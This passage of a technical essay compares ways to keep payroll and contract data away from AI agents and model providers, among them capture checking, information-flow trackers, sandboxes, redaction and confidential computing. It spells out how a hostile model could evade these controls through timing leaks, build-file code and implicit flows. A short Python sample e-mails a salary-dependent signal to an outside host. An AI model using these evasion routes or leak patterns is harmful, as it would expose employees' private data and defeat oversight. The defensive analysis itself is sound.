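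LACUNA's paper has a larger gap between summary and results. With DeepSeek V4 Flash, LACUNA solved 76.0% of 392 τ²-bench tasks, while ordinary tool calling solved 90.0%, or about 55 more tasks. Zhao and colleagues call this "on par". On the retail tasks, LACUNA solved 58.8% and tool calling 80.9%. With the weaker Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, the overall gap was smaller, at 29.1% against 33.2%. Zhao and colleagues ran each task once, so small differences may be chance, but 14 points across 392 tasks is too large to dismiss. TACIT's results on the same benchmark suggest that Scala alone doesn't explain the gap.

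The retry figures support the same conclusion. On τ²-bench, between 0.3% and 7.9% of the programs written for TACIT needed a retry, and those usually passed after one or two more attempts. With LACUNA and DeepSeek, the compiler rejected 22.4% of retail replies, and each retail task needed 7.1 new attempts on average. On a separate set of 830 research questions, the compiler rejected only 8.6%. It rejected 3.2% of the weaker Gemini model's replies in retail but 89% in telecoms, where the model made little progress.

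Many of these rejections had nothing to do with privacy. Agents often failed to handle missing values, or wrote a dollar sign in a way that Scala interprets as the start of a variable name. The published figures don't separate such errors from attempts to print private data. A firm using TACIT could separate them, because TACIT can save every program it receives. The firm could also estimate how often its model would have leaked data by accident, which the trials don't do, by counting the ordinary tasks in which the compiler rejects a printing function inside `map`.

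### What the compiler cannot check

The compiler protects only files marked as private. By default, TACIT marks common locations for passwords and keys, such as `.ssh` and `.env`. None of the default patterns matches `salaries.csv`, so a program could read the payroll as ordinary text and print it. Even if the firm adds that file, an export called `pay_march.csv` would be unprotected, so marking a whole folder is safer than marking single files. File names need separate protection, because TACIT's library returns them as ordinary text.

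Classifying everything isn't a solution either. VirtusLab, a software company that has written about safe mode, points out that agents are useful because they can read files and e-mails, so a firm that classifies too much loses most of the benefit.

TACIT also can't check what the agent does with other tools. The firm has to turn off the agent's built-in tools for reading files, running commands and opening web pages, or the agent can read the payroll without writing any Scala. The project's instructions for Claude Code list five tools to turn off, and its instructions for another agent, OpenCode, also block the search tools. A text search can print rows of the payroll too, so the firm should compare the project's list with the tools its agent has.

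Outside commands leave a similar gap, and an honest model could easily leak data through it. TACIT checks whether a program may run a command, but it returns the command's output as ordinary text. Odersky and colleagues advise allowing only specific safe commands, such as `git diff`, which shows recent changes to a project's files. A model might run `git diff` only to see what had changed, but if the firm keeps the payroll in that project and has just raised salaries, the output will include the old and new pay of everyone affected.

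Their other example is `sbt`, a tool that builds Scala programs. It runs code from the project's own build files, so a hostile model that can edit those files can run any code outside the compiler's checks. Scala Center's *Fixing a remote execution vulnerability in sbt* (2026) reports a separate flaw that allowed remote execution. The person who reported it had used AI to help audit the code. When the Scala Center asked Claude Fable 5 to look for vulnerabilities, a safeguard switched the request to an older model, which found the same flaw. A firm that fears a hostile model should therefore assume the model can find such flaws too.

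Timing leaks matter only if the model is hostile. Such a model could still use the 17 programs described earlier, which reveal a salary through their delays. Inside `map`, each program could calculate for a few seconds instead of pausing, and the compiler would accept the function because it would be pure. TACIT's optional time limit doesn't prevent this, because hitting the limit also reveals information.

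The design depends on the compiler and the library being correct. Capture checking is still experimental, and TACIT uses nightly versions of Scala, whose behaviour can change from day to day. Researchers have used computer-checked proofs to show that the basic theory of capture checking is sound, but Odersky and colleagues say that safe mode still needs a similar argument.

The same research group has already corrected a mistake in the type of `Try`, the standard Scala tool for catching errors, which TACIT uses to contain them. *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)* (Pham, Bračevac and colleagues, 2026) explains that the earlier type described the result as pure, although the result can raise the caught error again later. The new type records this, and the group proved the extended theory sound in Lean, a proof checker. They don't report that the mistake leaked any data. An honest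 model would rarely trigger such a mistake in a way that discloses a salary, but a hostile one could search for similar mistakes.

Setting up TACIT takes some work. The researchers have already published the reusable part, which is about 1,000 lines of Scala. A firm also needs code to connect it to its systems, which took the researchers a few hundred lines for each area in τ²-bench. Agents can draft this code, but someone who understands it has to review it, because everything else relies on it. The firm must also list its private files, permitted hosts and permitted commands, and keep those lists up to date.

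For the analyst, the biggest drawback may be giving up Python. Her firm's existing scripts use pandas, and TACIT can run them only as outside commands, which the compiler can't check. Zhao and colleagues acknowledge that their guarantees don't automatically carry over to Python, which most agent software uses. A firm that wants to keep its Python programs has to control the data while those programs run.

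## Tracking and restricting data while the code runs

A firm that keeps its Python scripts can control them from outside, either by limiting what a running program can reach or by tracking the payroll data as the program uses it. Limiting access takes much less work because operating systems already include the tools for it.

### A sandbox with a list of permitted hosts

A *sandbox* is a restricted environment in which a program can use only the files and network connections that someone has allowed. InfoQ (2026) describes Claude Code's version, which lets commands write inside the project folder and denies them network access by default, though the user can permit particular hosts. Anthropic argues that a sandbox has to limit both files and the network, because a program with open network access could send out any file it can read, and one with unrestricted file access could break out of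 the sandbox and regain the network.

If the sandbox's list of permitted hosts is empty, it blocks three of the nine ways the payroll could leak by accident. The program can't post the table to the charting company, install a package with an invented name or push `salaries.csv` to an outside repository. But programmers need access to some hosts, usually code repositories and package registries. Once the firm permits those, the program can again push the file and install the package, although a hostile package could contact only permitted hosts.

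The list can't distinguish good uses of a host from bad ones. According to Anthropic's documentation, Claude Code's proxy checks the name of the requested host but doesn't look inside encrypted traffic. It therefore treats downloading a library from a host the same as uploading a payroll to it. Kim, Trampert and colleagues (2026) point out in *FLOWSH* that fetching a public web page is normally harmless but becomes a leak if the address contains confidential data. A fixed list must therefore be too loose for some tasks or too strict for others.

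Most of the other routes don't require the program to have a network connection. The sandbox has to let the program read `salaries.csv`, and the harness sends the provider whatever the program prints. Both steps are permitted, and the second happens outside the sandbox. Anthropic warns that isolation doesn't change what goes to the model. Claude Code's built-in sandbox also covers only shell commands, so the agent's file-reading tool can open the payroll file from outside the sandbox. The firm could put the whole agent in a container, but the container would still need a connection to the provider.

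The best way to protect data from code running in a sandbox is to keep the data out of the sandbox. Willison (2026) quotes Anthropic's observation that credentials kept outside can't leak, whether the cause is a user, an attacker or a model finding a "creative" path. For the median task, the firm could copy only the department and pay columns into the sandbox. Printing the first five rows would still leak five salaries, but without names.

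### CaMeL's interpreter and the branch not taken

To let a program read the payroll without sending it on, the harness has to track which values came from the payroll. CaMeL (Debenedetti et al., 2025) does this with its own interpreter for a restricted form of Python. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (Tallam and Miller, 2025) describes the design. One model reads the user's request and writes a plan, and a second model handles untrusted content. The interpreter attaches to each value a record of where it came from and who may have it, and checks those records before every tool call. These records, called capabilities, work like taint labels.

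The planning model writes the whole plan before any tool runs, so the tools' results don't normally go back to it. The second model reads the text passed to it under the plan, so any provider hosting that model receives the text.

Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL's tracking misses some implicit flows. Their example, based on one that Fenton published in 1974, looks like this when adapted to the payroll:

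```python
above = True
below = True
if salary > 100000:
    below = False
if below:
    above = False
if above:
    send_email("someone@outside.example", "done")
```

CaMeL labels a variable when a branch that depends on private data changes it. For the lawyer, the first branch runs, so `below` becomes false and gets the payroll's label. The second test then fails, so `above = False` never runs and `above` stays true with no label. The last test appears to involve only public data, so CaMeL allows the e-mail. For someone who earns 52,000, `above` becomes false and no e-mail goes out. The recipient therefore learns whether the salary is above or below 100,000.

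No honest model would write that program, but the same gap appears in a very common pattern, where a program sets a default and then changes it:

```python
band = "standard"
if salary > 100000:
    band = "senior"
print(band)
```

Under the rule that Garby and colleagues describe, `band` has the payroll's label if the salary is above 100,000 and no label otherwise. A harness that sends only unlabelled output would send "standard" for the employee on 52,000 and withhold "senior" for the lawyer, and the missing answer would reveal as much as the one sent. As with other implicit flows, the firm can probably tolerate this leak for pay data when it happens outside a loop, but not for the column showing who is about to lose their job.

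Garby and colleagues briefly mention another gap that could matter more for honest code. When a CaMeL program inserts an untrusted value into a piece of text, the result counts as trusted. They don't say whether the value also loses its restrictions on who can read it. If it does, an ordinary line such as `f"Legal median: {median}"` would remove the payroll's label from the lawyer's salary. A firm that adopts CaMeL should test that line before Fenton's.

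Their own language, LLMbda, stops a program that tries to add to a public conversation from inside a branch that depends on private data. They used the proof checker Lean to prove that secrets can't influence public results in any LLMbda program, except by affecting whether the program finishes. The guarantee covers programs that a model writes during the run, but not Python programs.

### Fides and the trusted context

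Fides labels each piece of data with the people who may read it. If the analyst and the head of human resources may read the payroll, and the analyst and the head of sales may read the sales figures, then only the analyst may read a report based on both. Fides also labels data as trusted or untrusted, depending on whether an outsider could have tampered with it.

Costa and colleagues give two rules that a system can enforce with these labels. The first permits an important action only if the decision to take it is based entirely on trusted data. The second permits sending data only if every recipient is allowed to read it. A designer can require both rules or accept an action that satisfies either one.

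Accepting either one is a poor choice for a model that makes mistakes. If everything in the context is trusted, the model may send anything to anyone, because such a release, according to Costa and colleagues, "can be assumed to be intentional". The analyst's firm trusts its payroll staff not to plant instructions, so the model's context would normally be trusted. If the model attached the whole payroll to an e-mail for the wrong person, the system would allow it.

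Microsoft's article on information-flow control includes a sample policy of this kind for messages to a Teams channel. The policy allows any message from a trusted context without checking who is in the channel. The article also describes how labels would stop the agent from telling Marco the sales figures, since Marco isn't among the readers of Priya's e-mail. But the labels wouldn't stop the leak if the firm treated colleagues' e-mail as trusted and used a policy like the sample, so the firm should require the second rule every time.

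Fides doesn't check the data sent to the model, because its designers assumed nobody hostile could see that data. Costa and colleagues note that the check can run earlier, so that it also covers requests to the model. The firm could then list the provider as a reader of the column names and permitted medians, but not of the payroll. Fides can also store a tool's result in a variable and show the model only the variable's name. Costa and colleagues used this in their tests to hide untrusted data, so the firm would have to extend it to confidential data.

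### One salary's path through GAAP

GAAP treats the provider as an outside party from the start. Its models write plans in a small language that contains only tool calls and comparisons. Stanley and colleagues chose this over Python because existing tools for tracking data in Python are incomplete or unsound. In simplified form, a plan for the salary task might be:

```
1  read_file("salaries.csv")
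2  department_medians(result of 1)
3  access_data("hr_head_email")
4  send_email(to: result of 3, body: result of 2)
5  multishot_call("Explain these to the analyst", result of 2)
```

`department_medians` is a tool on the analyst's machine that the firm would have to add. The lawyer's 118,000 moves through the plan as follows.

In step 1, GAAP reads the file and labels its text `salaries.csv`. The model that wrote the plan hasn't seen the text.

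In step 2, the lawyer's pay becomes the Legal median, and the result inherits the label. GAAP doesn't need to prompt anyone about this step if the firm has marked the tool as allowed to access all private data, as GAAP already treats the file system.

Step 3 fetches an address from the *private-data store*, where GAAP keeps personal details under names such as `hr_head_email`. The model has access to the names but not the values. If the store has no such entry, GAAP prompts the analyst to supply one.

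Step 4 would disclose the figure, so GAAP checks its *permission records*. Each record allows or forbids sending one piece of private data to one outside party. On the first run no record exists, so GAAP pauses and asks the analyst whether the contents of `salaries.csv` may go to the head of human resources. It saves her answer unless she chooses to allow the transfer just once. The published sample description of the mail tool identifies the outside party by the recipient's address, so the question wouldn't name the mail company, even though the firm's rule forbids sharing the figures with that company. The firm would need to write a stricter description of the tool.

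After the e-mail goes out, GAAP records the transfer in its *disclosure log*, including the time, the recipient and the values sent. If the agent finds the medians in the sent mail a week later, GAAP uses the log to put the payroll's label back on them.

Step 5 calls the model to continue with the medians in its context, which would send the 118,000 to the provider for the first time. GAAP checks the permission records again, this time for the provider as the outside party. If there is no answer on file, it asks the analyst. If she refuses, the call returns an error that also carries the payroll's label, so that later steps can't pass on the fact that she refused. If she agrees, the provider gets all four medians, and GAAP labels every tool call in the model's next plan as derived from the payroll.

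Her answer covers more than she may realise, because the label records that the medians came from `salaries.csv` but not how much of the file's data they contain. If she lets the provider have the medians and GAAP saves that permission, a later plan could send the provider every row without her being asked again. An honest model could easily do that while checking how the salaries are formatted. Choosing "just once" prevents this, but she then has to answer the question every time.

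GAAP has a better solution, which is to let a tool's description give its result a new label instead of inheriting the old one. In an example by Stanley and colleagues, ordering food produces data labelled as an order receipt. The firm could label the output of `department_medians` with the tool's name and let the provider receive only data with that label. The tool would then have to leave out small departments itself, since GAAP would no longer treat its output as payroll data.

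When code branches on private data, GAAP also tracks the branch that doesn't run. It labels every instruction in both branches, up to the point where they meet again.

### Coding agents that use a shell

GAAP needs tools with known effects, but the effects of a coding agent's shell commands aren't known in advance. A command such as `python report.py` can open any number of files and contact any number of hosts. Kim and colleagues built Flowsh to observe what a command does instead of predicting it.

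Flowsh runs each command in a sandbox. A monitor in the operating system records every file the command opens, and a proxy handles every connection. Flowsh combines the labels of all these inputs into one label for the whole command. It checks each network request against that label before sending it, because a request can't be undone once sent. It holds file changes in a separate layer and checks them when the command ends, so the user can approve or discard them together. The label stays with any file the command writes, even after a restart, so a summary of confidential payroll data is still labeled confidential the next day.

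Flowsh assigns one label to each command, which is crude. If a script opens the payroll and then downloads a font for a chart, Flowsh treats the download as a possible leak, even though the request contains no salaries. The agent can avoid this by downloading the font in a separate command before opening the payroll.

Like Microsoft's sample, Flowsh's default policy has an exception that lets a command send data anywhere if it has read only trusted data. As a result, labelling the payroll file correctly can remove its protection. In the example configuration, a file without a label counts as untrusted and readable only by the user, so Flowsh would block the analyst's program if it read an unlabelled `salaries.csv` and tried to post it to the charting company. If the firm then labelled the file as confidential, and as trusted because only payroll staff can edit it, Flowsh would allow the request.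 The firm can avoid this by deleting the exception, which Kim and colleagues recommend for catching a model's own mistakes.

Flowsh labels a command's printed output but doesn't treat the provider as a reader, so the harness would have to check that label before adding the output to the context.

### What tracking costs

All four systems reduce the number of tasks that agents complete. The table shows results for three of them on tasks without attacks. The rows aren't comparable because the tasks and models differ.

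| System and tasks | Model | Completed without checks | Completed with checks |
|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL, banking, run by Garby and colleagues | GPT-5.2 | 66.7% | 37.5% |
| Fides, average of four areas | GPT-4o | 84.3% | 50.0% |
| Flowsh, office tasks, with someone to approve requests | GPT-6.2 Sol | 96.1% | 88.2% |
| Flowsh, office tasks, with nobody to approve requests | GPT-6.2 Sol | 94.1% | 58.8% |

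The first figure for CaMeL is for CaMeL with its policy checks off, while the first figure for Fides is for an ordinary agent. When Costa and colleagues applied Fides's checks to that agent, it completed only 41.9% of tasks, so Fides recovers some of the tasks lost to the checks. Fides's lead over the ordinary agent with checks was 8 points with GPT-4o and 16 points with o1, a stronger model. Both models are now old, and current ones would probably do better.

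CaMeL's 37.5% is also lower than its banking results in Odersky and colleagues' tests, which used other models. CaMeL seems unusually sensitive to the choice of model. Stanley and colleagues ran CaMeL with GPT-5 because it did much worse with the newer GPT-5.6 Sol.

GAAP completed two fewer of its designers' 20 tasks than an unprotected agent. It did about as well as that agent on AgentDojo and 10% worse on AgentDyn, a benchmark in which plans often have to change midway. One purchase failed because the plan prohibited retrying the checkout, and the shop then asked for a one-time code and a second attempt. In the AgentDojo and AgentDyn runs, Stanley and colleagues assumed that the user approved every disclosure, so those results show how GAAP's planning language affects performance but not how refusing disclosures would.

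GAAP is also slow and expensive. Tasks on the two benchmarks took an average of 188 seconds with GAAP, compared with 28 seconds for the unprotected agent, and the cost of running the whole set rose from $28 to $81. Flowsh added 17% to 34% to the running time.

These systems worked well against attacks in tests. With its checks on, Fides stopped all the genuine attacks on AgentDojo, where 152 had succeeded against the ordinary agent. CaMeL with checks blocked every attack in the runs that finished. GAAP blocked all seven kinds of attack tried against it, and Flowsh blocked all 40 attack runs with nobody approving requests. None of these tests measured honest mistakes. The systems would catch many of them, but how often they would do so in ordinary work is unknown.

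### Releasing a figure on purpose

A tracker that never removes a label soon stops all useful work, because every result derived from the payroll stays as confidential as the payroll. Sooner or later the firm has to declassify something. Its rule allows medians for departments of at least five people, which it could write as a trusted function:

```python
def releasable_medians(staff, minimum=5):
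    pay = staff.groupby("department")["annual_pay"]
    return pay.median()[pay.count() >= minimum]
```

The function leaves out Legal, whose median is the lawyer's salary. A provider that knows the department exists can still infer from the output that Legal has fewer than five salaries on file.

A minimum group size doesn't prevent leaks across a series of releases. Suppose the firm also allows totals, and a report gives Engineering's total pay as 840,000 for twelve people. One of them leaves, and the next report gives 775,000 for eleven. Both groups meet the minimum, but if nobody else's pay has changed, the difference of 65,000 is the salary of the person who left. This can happen even when the model and the tracker work correctly, because both totals carry the same label and the same permission covers them.

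Averages have the same weakness, because multiplying an average by the number of people gives the total. Rounding to the nearest thousand helps, because both averages become 70,000 and the missing salary could then be anywhere between about 58,500 and 81,500.

Medians are safer than totals, but they also leak data. The median of eleven salaries is somebody's exact salary, say 68,000. If a twelfth person is added, the median becomes the midpoint between 68,000 and another salary. If that midpoint is 67,000, the other salary must be 66,000. The provider then knows two exact salaries, though not whose they are.

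The release function could keep a list of the groups it has already reported and refuse any group that differs from an earlier one by fewer than five people. GAAP's disclosure log is a natural starting point, although it records the values sent, not who was in each group. An individual's salary can still leak under this rule. Suppose a department of 21 people consists of two teams of ten and one head. The salary totals for each team and for the department all pass, because any two of these groups differ by at least ten people, but subtracting both team totals from the department total gives the head's salary. For routine reports, the firm would do better to fix the groups and dates in advance and have someone check all the figures together.

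Some systems release small answers automatically. Fides, for example, can let a yes/no result through because it carries so little information. Garby and colleagues object that nobody can then distinguish an intended release from a leak that takes the same form. In their design, LLMbda, a program can change a label only with an explicit instruction, which a reviewer can find. They tested this for trust labels by letting an agent mark a file's contents as trusted so that it could act on them. With one model, removing that option cut the share of completed banking tasks from 75% to 62.5%. They also proved that an instruction that changes a trust label can't weaken the protection of secrets.

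### Who approves a release

When no rule covers a release, most of these systems ask the user. Claude Code used to ask about individual actions, and InfoQ reports that users approved roughly 93% of the requests. Most requests were probably harmless, so this figure doesn't show how often users approved dangerous ones. But according to Kim and colleagues, Anthropic also found that users paid less attention as requests accumulated. Adding the sandbox reduced requests by 84%.

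Tracking data can further reduce the number of approval requests. Flowsh made 1.2 requests per completed office task, compared with 6.7 without tracking. GAAP averaged 1.5 per task, down from 3.8 without its saved permissions. For one task early in the test, saved permissions cut the number of requests from 57 to 7. Of the 57 requests without them, 14 were about sharing data with the model. At 1.5 requests per task, someone running 20 tasks a day would still be interrupted 30 times.

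Flowsh's result depends on an ideal approver who refused any action that an attack had influenced and approved everything else, which would include honest mistakes. Kim and colleagues acknowledge that nobody has tested whether the information Flowsh provides helps real people decide correctly.

The wording of the approval request probably matters a lot. An analyst has no basis for judging "Allow `python report.py`?" but can easily answer "Send the provider the Legal median, which is one person's salary?" A tracker can supply the source and the recipient, and Microsoft's dialogs are meant to highlight both. Adding that Legal has only one employee requires a function written for the payroll data.

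The analyst may also be the wrong person to ask. GAAP was designed for personal assistants, whose users decide about their own data. The payroll contains other people's pay, and the firm has already decided that the provider may not have it. I would let the payroll office set the standing permissions. The analyst could then refuse a release or refer it to that office, but could not grant a new permission.

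Another option is to have a model decide. FlowSeal, the defence in *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow*, intercepts every attempt to write or share something, even if the agent hasn't noticed a privacy risk. When necessary, a separate model call compares the protected records with the proposed output. Across the attacks tested, 0% to 3.3% of the private items leaked, and the agent completed 72.4% of ordinary tasks, compared with 75.9% for the best of the other defences. Having a model decide spares the analyst many questions, but that model has to read the private records.

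### What an honest model lets each design leave out

If the firm is confident that its model is honest and that no outsider can plant text in the model's context, it can simplify all five designs.

| Design | What the firm could leave out | What it still needs |
|---|---|---|
| Sandbox | Extra barriers against deliberate escape, such as a separate virtual machine | A short list of hosts, and a separate control on output that goes to the model |
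| CaMeL | Labels for branches on ordinary values, outside loops | Labels on copied values and on text that contains them, and on branches that test yes/no fields |
| Fides | The labels for trusted and untrusted data | The check on readers for every transfer, with the provider included |
| GAAP | Labels on the errors that follow a refusal | The provider as an outside party, narrow permissions and the disclosure log |
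| Flowsh | Protection of the stored labels against tampering by the agent | The check on readers, without the exception for trusted data |

Fides and Flowsh use trust labels to stop prompt injection, so the firm should drop the labels only if nobody outside the firm can write text that the model reads. The newly acquired company's payroll records would be a reason to keep them.

Fides and Flowsh need a stricter policy for trusted contexts if they are meant to prevent honest mistakes. When attackers are the only concern, the policy can let trusted contexts send confidential data, which avoids many questions. Most mistakes happen in trusted contexts, so a policy meant to prevent them can't make this exception. Nobody has measured the effects of removing it, but Kim and colleagues expect more requests and fewer completed tasks. Flowsh completed all 15 office runs that used confidential data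 from trusted sources without asking any questions. Without the exception, it would have to ask whenever such a run sent data to a host that wasn't an authorised reader.

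## Letting a model read the private content

The defences so far work best when the model can write its program without seeing the data. That works for computing medians, but not when the analyst wants a summary of the unusual terms in the lawyer's employment contract. No program written in advance can find those terms, because something has to read the text and judge what is unusual. The contract contains her salary of 118,000, her notice period and a clause about her leaving in May.

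The firm has four options. It can run its own model, disguise the text before sending it, use remote computers designed to keep their operator from reading the text, or send everything and rely on the provider's promises about storage.

### A trusted local model

TACIT lets a program pass text to a second model that the firm trusts, usually one on its own machine. The function for this is called `chat`, and it comes in two versions. The first takes ordinary text and returns ordinary text. The second takes text in the `Classified` wrapper and returns the reply in the same wrapper. For the employment contract, the hosted model could write:

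```scala
requestFileSystem("/contracts") {
  val contract = readClassified("/contracts/legal.txt")
  println(chat("List the unusual terms in this contract.", contract))
}
```

The local model reads the contract and writes a summary for the analyst, while the hosted model receives only asterisks. In tests by Odersky and colleagues, agents used this function to summarise a confidential incident report and to anonymise employee reviews. The local model has no tools, so an instruction hidden in the contract could distort the summary but couldn't make the model send an e-mail.

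However, the hosted model can't check the result. If the local model overlooks the clause about May, the analyst will notice only if she reads the contract herself. The firm also shouldn't unwrap a summary just because a search finds no salary in it, since a model's output can carry traces of a secret that doesn't appear in the text.

Sometimes the firm needs code that depends on what a document contains. Suppose it wants the notice period from 200 contracts with different layouts. The hosted model can't write one function that anticipates all of them. LACUNA lets that function call a local model when it runs:

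```scala
contract.map { content =>
  local.agent[Int]("Find the notice period in days")
}
```

The hosted model writes these lines without access to `content`. When the program reaches the inner call, the local model reads the contract and writes code for its layout. The compiler then checks the new code under the same rule as the surrounding function, so the code can't print, open a file or contact the hosted model. Zhao and colleagues say this adds flexibility without reducing safety.

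If the local model runs out of attempts, LACUNA raises an error containing the compiler's messages. Those messages could quote code that the local model wrote after reading the contract, such as a comparison with 118,000. The firm should keep this error from reaching the hosted model. LACUNA also has a version of the call that returns a failure as an ordinary value, which `map` would wrap.

### What local serving software leaves behind

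TACIT's types can't guarantee that the local model retains none of the contract. Odersky and colleagues leave that to the harness, which has to use a model service that doesn't carry text from one request into the next. Otherwise, a later call to the first version of `chat` might return part of the contract as ordinary text, which the hosted model could read.

In *The Illusion of Local Privacy*, Ibrahim, Ikram and Salama (2026) examined what popular local serving software does with prompts. They put a unique marker in each prompt and searched memory, files and other users' sessions for it.

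In one test, 12 users took turns on the same server process, and the researchers then recovered 110 copies of prompts from 11 of them. Changing the software to clear some of the places where it kept prompts reduced the copies to 78, but prompts from 11 users were still there. In a separate test, the researchers found no markers in the memory they examined after shutting the server down. Restarting it after each confidential job is therefore a sensible precaution, although the test didn't show whether the computer had physically erased the text.

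LM Studio, a desktop program for running models, also wrote prompts to a plaintext log, where they remained days later. The installation that Ibrahim and colleagues tested had the `logSensitiveData` setting turned on. After they turned it off and restarted the program, new prompts no longer appeared in the files they searched. They found no such copies from Ollama, a similar program.

Sharing a server created further problems. llama.cpp, which many local tools use to run models, has an optional feature that saves conversations to disk. With it turned on, a user with a valid key could restore another user's conversation in all 200 trials, and the model then repeated that user's secret in 126 of them. The server also answers faster when it has already processed the start of a prompt, so a user could guess the opening of a colleague's document and check the guess by timing the response. With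 one model, the first word arrived after 20 milliseconds instead of 786.

None of these leaks sends anything to a hosted provider. Ibrahim et al. monitored 205 Ollama sessions and saw no outside connections. The people who could benefit from the leaks are colleagues on a shared server and anyone whose software runs under the analyst's account.

A hosted coding agent may be one of the programs running under her account, though. If she asks it why the local model is slow, it might print the last lines of the log, and the harness would send the contract text in them to the provider. An honest model could easily make this mistake. The firm should turn off the log and mark the serving software's folder as private. It should also make sure the server can't be reached from the internet. Ibrahim and colleagues counted 32,723 Ollama servers that could be on 4 July 2026.

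### Disguising the text before it leaves

If a small local model can't summarise a difficult contract well enough, the firm may want to use a stronger hosted one. LLM-Redactor can change the text before it leaves the machine. Agyemang and colleagues compared eight techniques on 1,300 artificial prompts in which they had marked 4,014 sensitive details. The table shows the share of those details that left the machine in full or in part, counting any matching run of four characters as a partial leak. Identifying descriptions are phrases that point to a person without naming them, such as "the firm's only lawyer".

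| Technique | Personal details in prose | Identifying descriptions | Private code |
|---|---|---|---|
| Local answering: a small model handles simple requests and the rest go out unchanged | 6.3% | 46.8% | 59.9% |
| Redaction: placeholders replace detected details | 15.3% | 95.0% | 58.5% |
| Redaction, then rephrasing by a local model | 13.9% | 94.1% | 55.8% |
| Redaction, then random changes to a few words | 17.6% | 95.0% | 51.7% |
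| Attested hardware: a protected remote machine reads the full text | 100% | 100% | 100% |
| Split model: the first layers run locally | 0% | 0% | 0% |
| Homomorphic encryption: the provider computes on encrypted text | 0% | 0% | 0% |
| Secret sharing: several servers each hold a meaningless part | 0% | 0% | 0% |
| Local answering, redaction and rephrasing together | 0.6% | 43.6% | 31.3% |

The 100% for attested hardware counts text that the hardware is supposed to protect after it arrives. The three rows of zeros are weaker evidence than they look, because Agyemang and colleagues only simulated those techniques. Their secret-sharing example hides only the first step of the model's computation and leaves the other layers exposed. With a split model, the provider may be able to reconstruct the text from the numbers it receives. Computing on encrypted text offers mathematically strong protection,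 but Agyemang and colleagues estimate that it is 10,000 to 100,000 times slower than ordinary processing for models of a useful size.

The combination in the last row gives the best practical result, but its 0.6% depends heavily on the small model answering prompts locally. The small model answered 94.4% of the prompts with personal details, so only 28 of 500 went to the provider. It answered 38% of the prompts with code. The quality tests compared redacted prompts with unredacted ones, so they didn't measure the quality of the small model's answers.

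Redaction alone made answers worse. In 50 comparisons on prose, a judge model rated the answer to the original prompt higher 78% of the time. Agyemang and colleagues call this loss in quality modest, which seems to understate it, although the judge was a small model. Redaction took less than 30 milliseconds for a typical prompt, while rephrasing took about two seconds.

For the employment contract, redaction might replace the lawyer's name with `PERSON_1` but leave "the firm's only lawyer" next to the salary of 118,000. The detector looks for names, addresses, keys and similar details, so the firm would have to add a rule for salaries. One such rule, a pattern for employee numbers, cut their leak rate from 79.8% to zero. But the salary may be one of the unusual terms the analyst asked about, and the model can't include it in a summary if it has been redacted.

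Rephrasing a prompt doesn't stop its descriptions from identifying a person or organisation. In a test with 20 prompts, another model judged that 95% of the originals identified the same person or organisation, and that all of them did after redaction and rephrasing. Agyemang and colleagues conclude that these methods can remove words but can't remove the meaning without making the prompt useless. Their decision rule still gives the combined method a leak rate of at most 0.5% on such descriptions, but the firm shouldn't rely on this figure because it counts a leak only when the marked phrase is repeated exactly.

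Choosing which requests to send can also reveal private information. Suppose the harness keeps contracts with medical clauses on the local machine and sends the rest. A provider that expects twelve contracts and receives eleven can guess that the missing one has a medical clause. *AVEC* (Gaikwad, 2025) proves that no fixed rule of this kind can satisfy *differential privacy*, a standard limit on how much one private detail may change what an observer sees. A randomized rule can satisfy it, but the harness would then sometimes send a request that it would otherwise have kept local.

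### Asking for advice without the details

When the firm needs help with a technical problem, the provider may not need the private text. Suppose a local agent is repairing the payroll program and gets stuck on the cell containing "118000 until she leaves in May". It could quote the cell to a hosted model, but it would probably get the same advice by asking how to handle a numeric column in which some cells contain notes.

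In *Teaching Code Agents to Ask Without Leaking Private Code*, Jiang, Shi and colleagues (2026) trained a small local agent to ask the second kind of question, using a method they call *utility-verified abstraction*. They first collected questions that the agent had asked a hosted expert during successful repairs. Another model rewrote each question, replacing private names with descriptions of their role and type. The researchers then returned the repair to the point where the agent had asked the question, sent the expert the rewritten version and let the agent continue. They kept a rewritten question for training only if it disclosed fewer private names and the repair still succeeded.

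The table shows the results on 500 real software issues, with DeepSeek-V3.2 as the expert. Private names include identifiers in the code, file names and paths.

| Agent | Issues solved | Runs that consulted the expert | Private names per question |
|---|---|---|---|
| Untrained, no expert | 25.3% | 0% | none sent |
| Untrained, with expert | 24.6% | 4.8% | 4.42 |
| Untrained, told to protect privacy | 23.8% | 1.4% | 4.64 |
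| Untrained, with automatic placeholders | 25.0% | 4.6% | 0.97 |
| Trained | 37.6% | 7.4% | 1.20 |

Telling the agent to protect privacy made it ask fewer questions, but those questions disclosed slightly more on average. Jiang and colleagues call this "privacy by silence". A firm that measured only total disclosure would think the instruction had worked. Automatic placeholders hid the most names but left more of the surrounding code in the questions.

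In a separate comparison with Claude Opus 4.8 as the expert, dropping the step in which the repair has to succeed again reduced the share of issues solved from 40.6% to 22.4%. The agent then disclosed even fewer names, probably because it had learned to leave out details that the expert needed.

Most of the improvement came without the expert's help. The trained agent solved 36.2% of the issues on its own, and consulting DeepSeek added only 1.4 percentage points. A firm with strict privacy rules could reasonably use the trained agent alone. Consultation cost up to $0.48 per 1,000 tasks, compared with about $268 for running the local agent.

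The method protects names and copied code, but Jiang and colleagues don't try to prevent a provider from inferring private facts from a general question. The method also suits code repairs better than contracts, because a programmer can describe a fault in general terms, whereas a contract's unusual terms are themselves the private content.

### Remote computers that hide data from their operator

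*Confidential computing* keeps the text readable to the model but hides it from the company that owns the machine. The hardware runs the program in a *trusted execution environment*, an isolated area that even the machine's operating system can't read.

Before sending the contract, the analyst's software asks for a signed statement about the remote machine, a check called *remote attestation*. According to *When Agents Handle Secrets* (Forough, Kogias and Haddadi, 2026), the check can confirm that the hardware is genuine, the firmware has a known version and patch level, and the expected program is running. If the statement is wrong, the software doesn't send the contract.

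Attestation confirms that the expected program is running, but it doesn't show that the program is safe. A program that saves every prompt to an outside log would still pass. Someone therefore has to inspect the program and make sure that the attested version is the one they inspected. Forough and colleagues also warn that protecting the model doesn't automatically protect the rest of an agent. Its stored memory, tools and connections to other agents may lie outside the protected area. If the remote agent puts a sentence from the contract into a web search, the search company receives it.

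Apple and Google have both built large systems of this kind. Apple's Private Cloud Compute handles requests too demanding for a phone or laptop. Help Net Security's *Apple extends Private Cloud Compute to third-party data centers* lists its main requirements, including keeping no data after a request, giving staff no privileged access while the system runs, and making it impossible to target a particular user. In June 2026, Apple announced it was extending the system to Google's data centres. Willison notes that the models there are versions of Google's Gemini and run on NVIDIA hardware.

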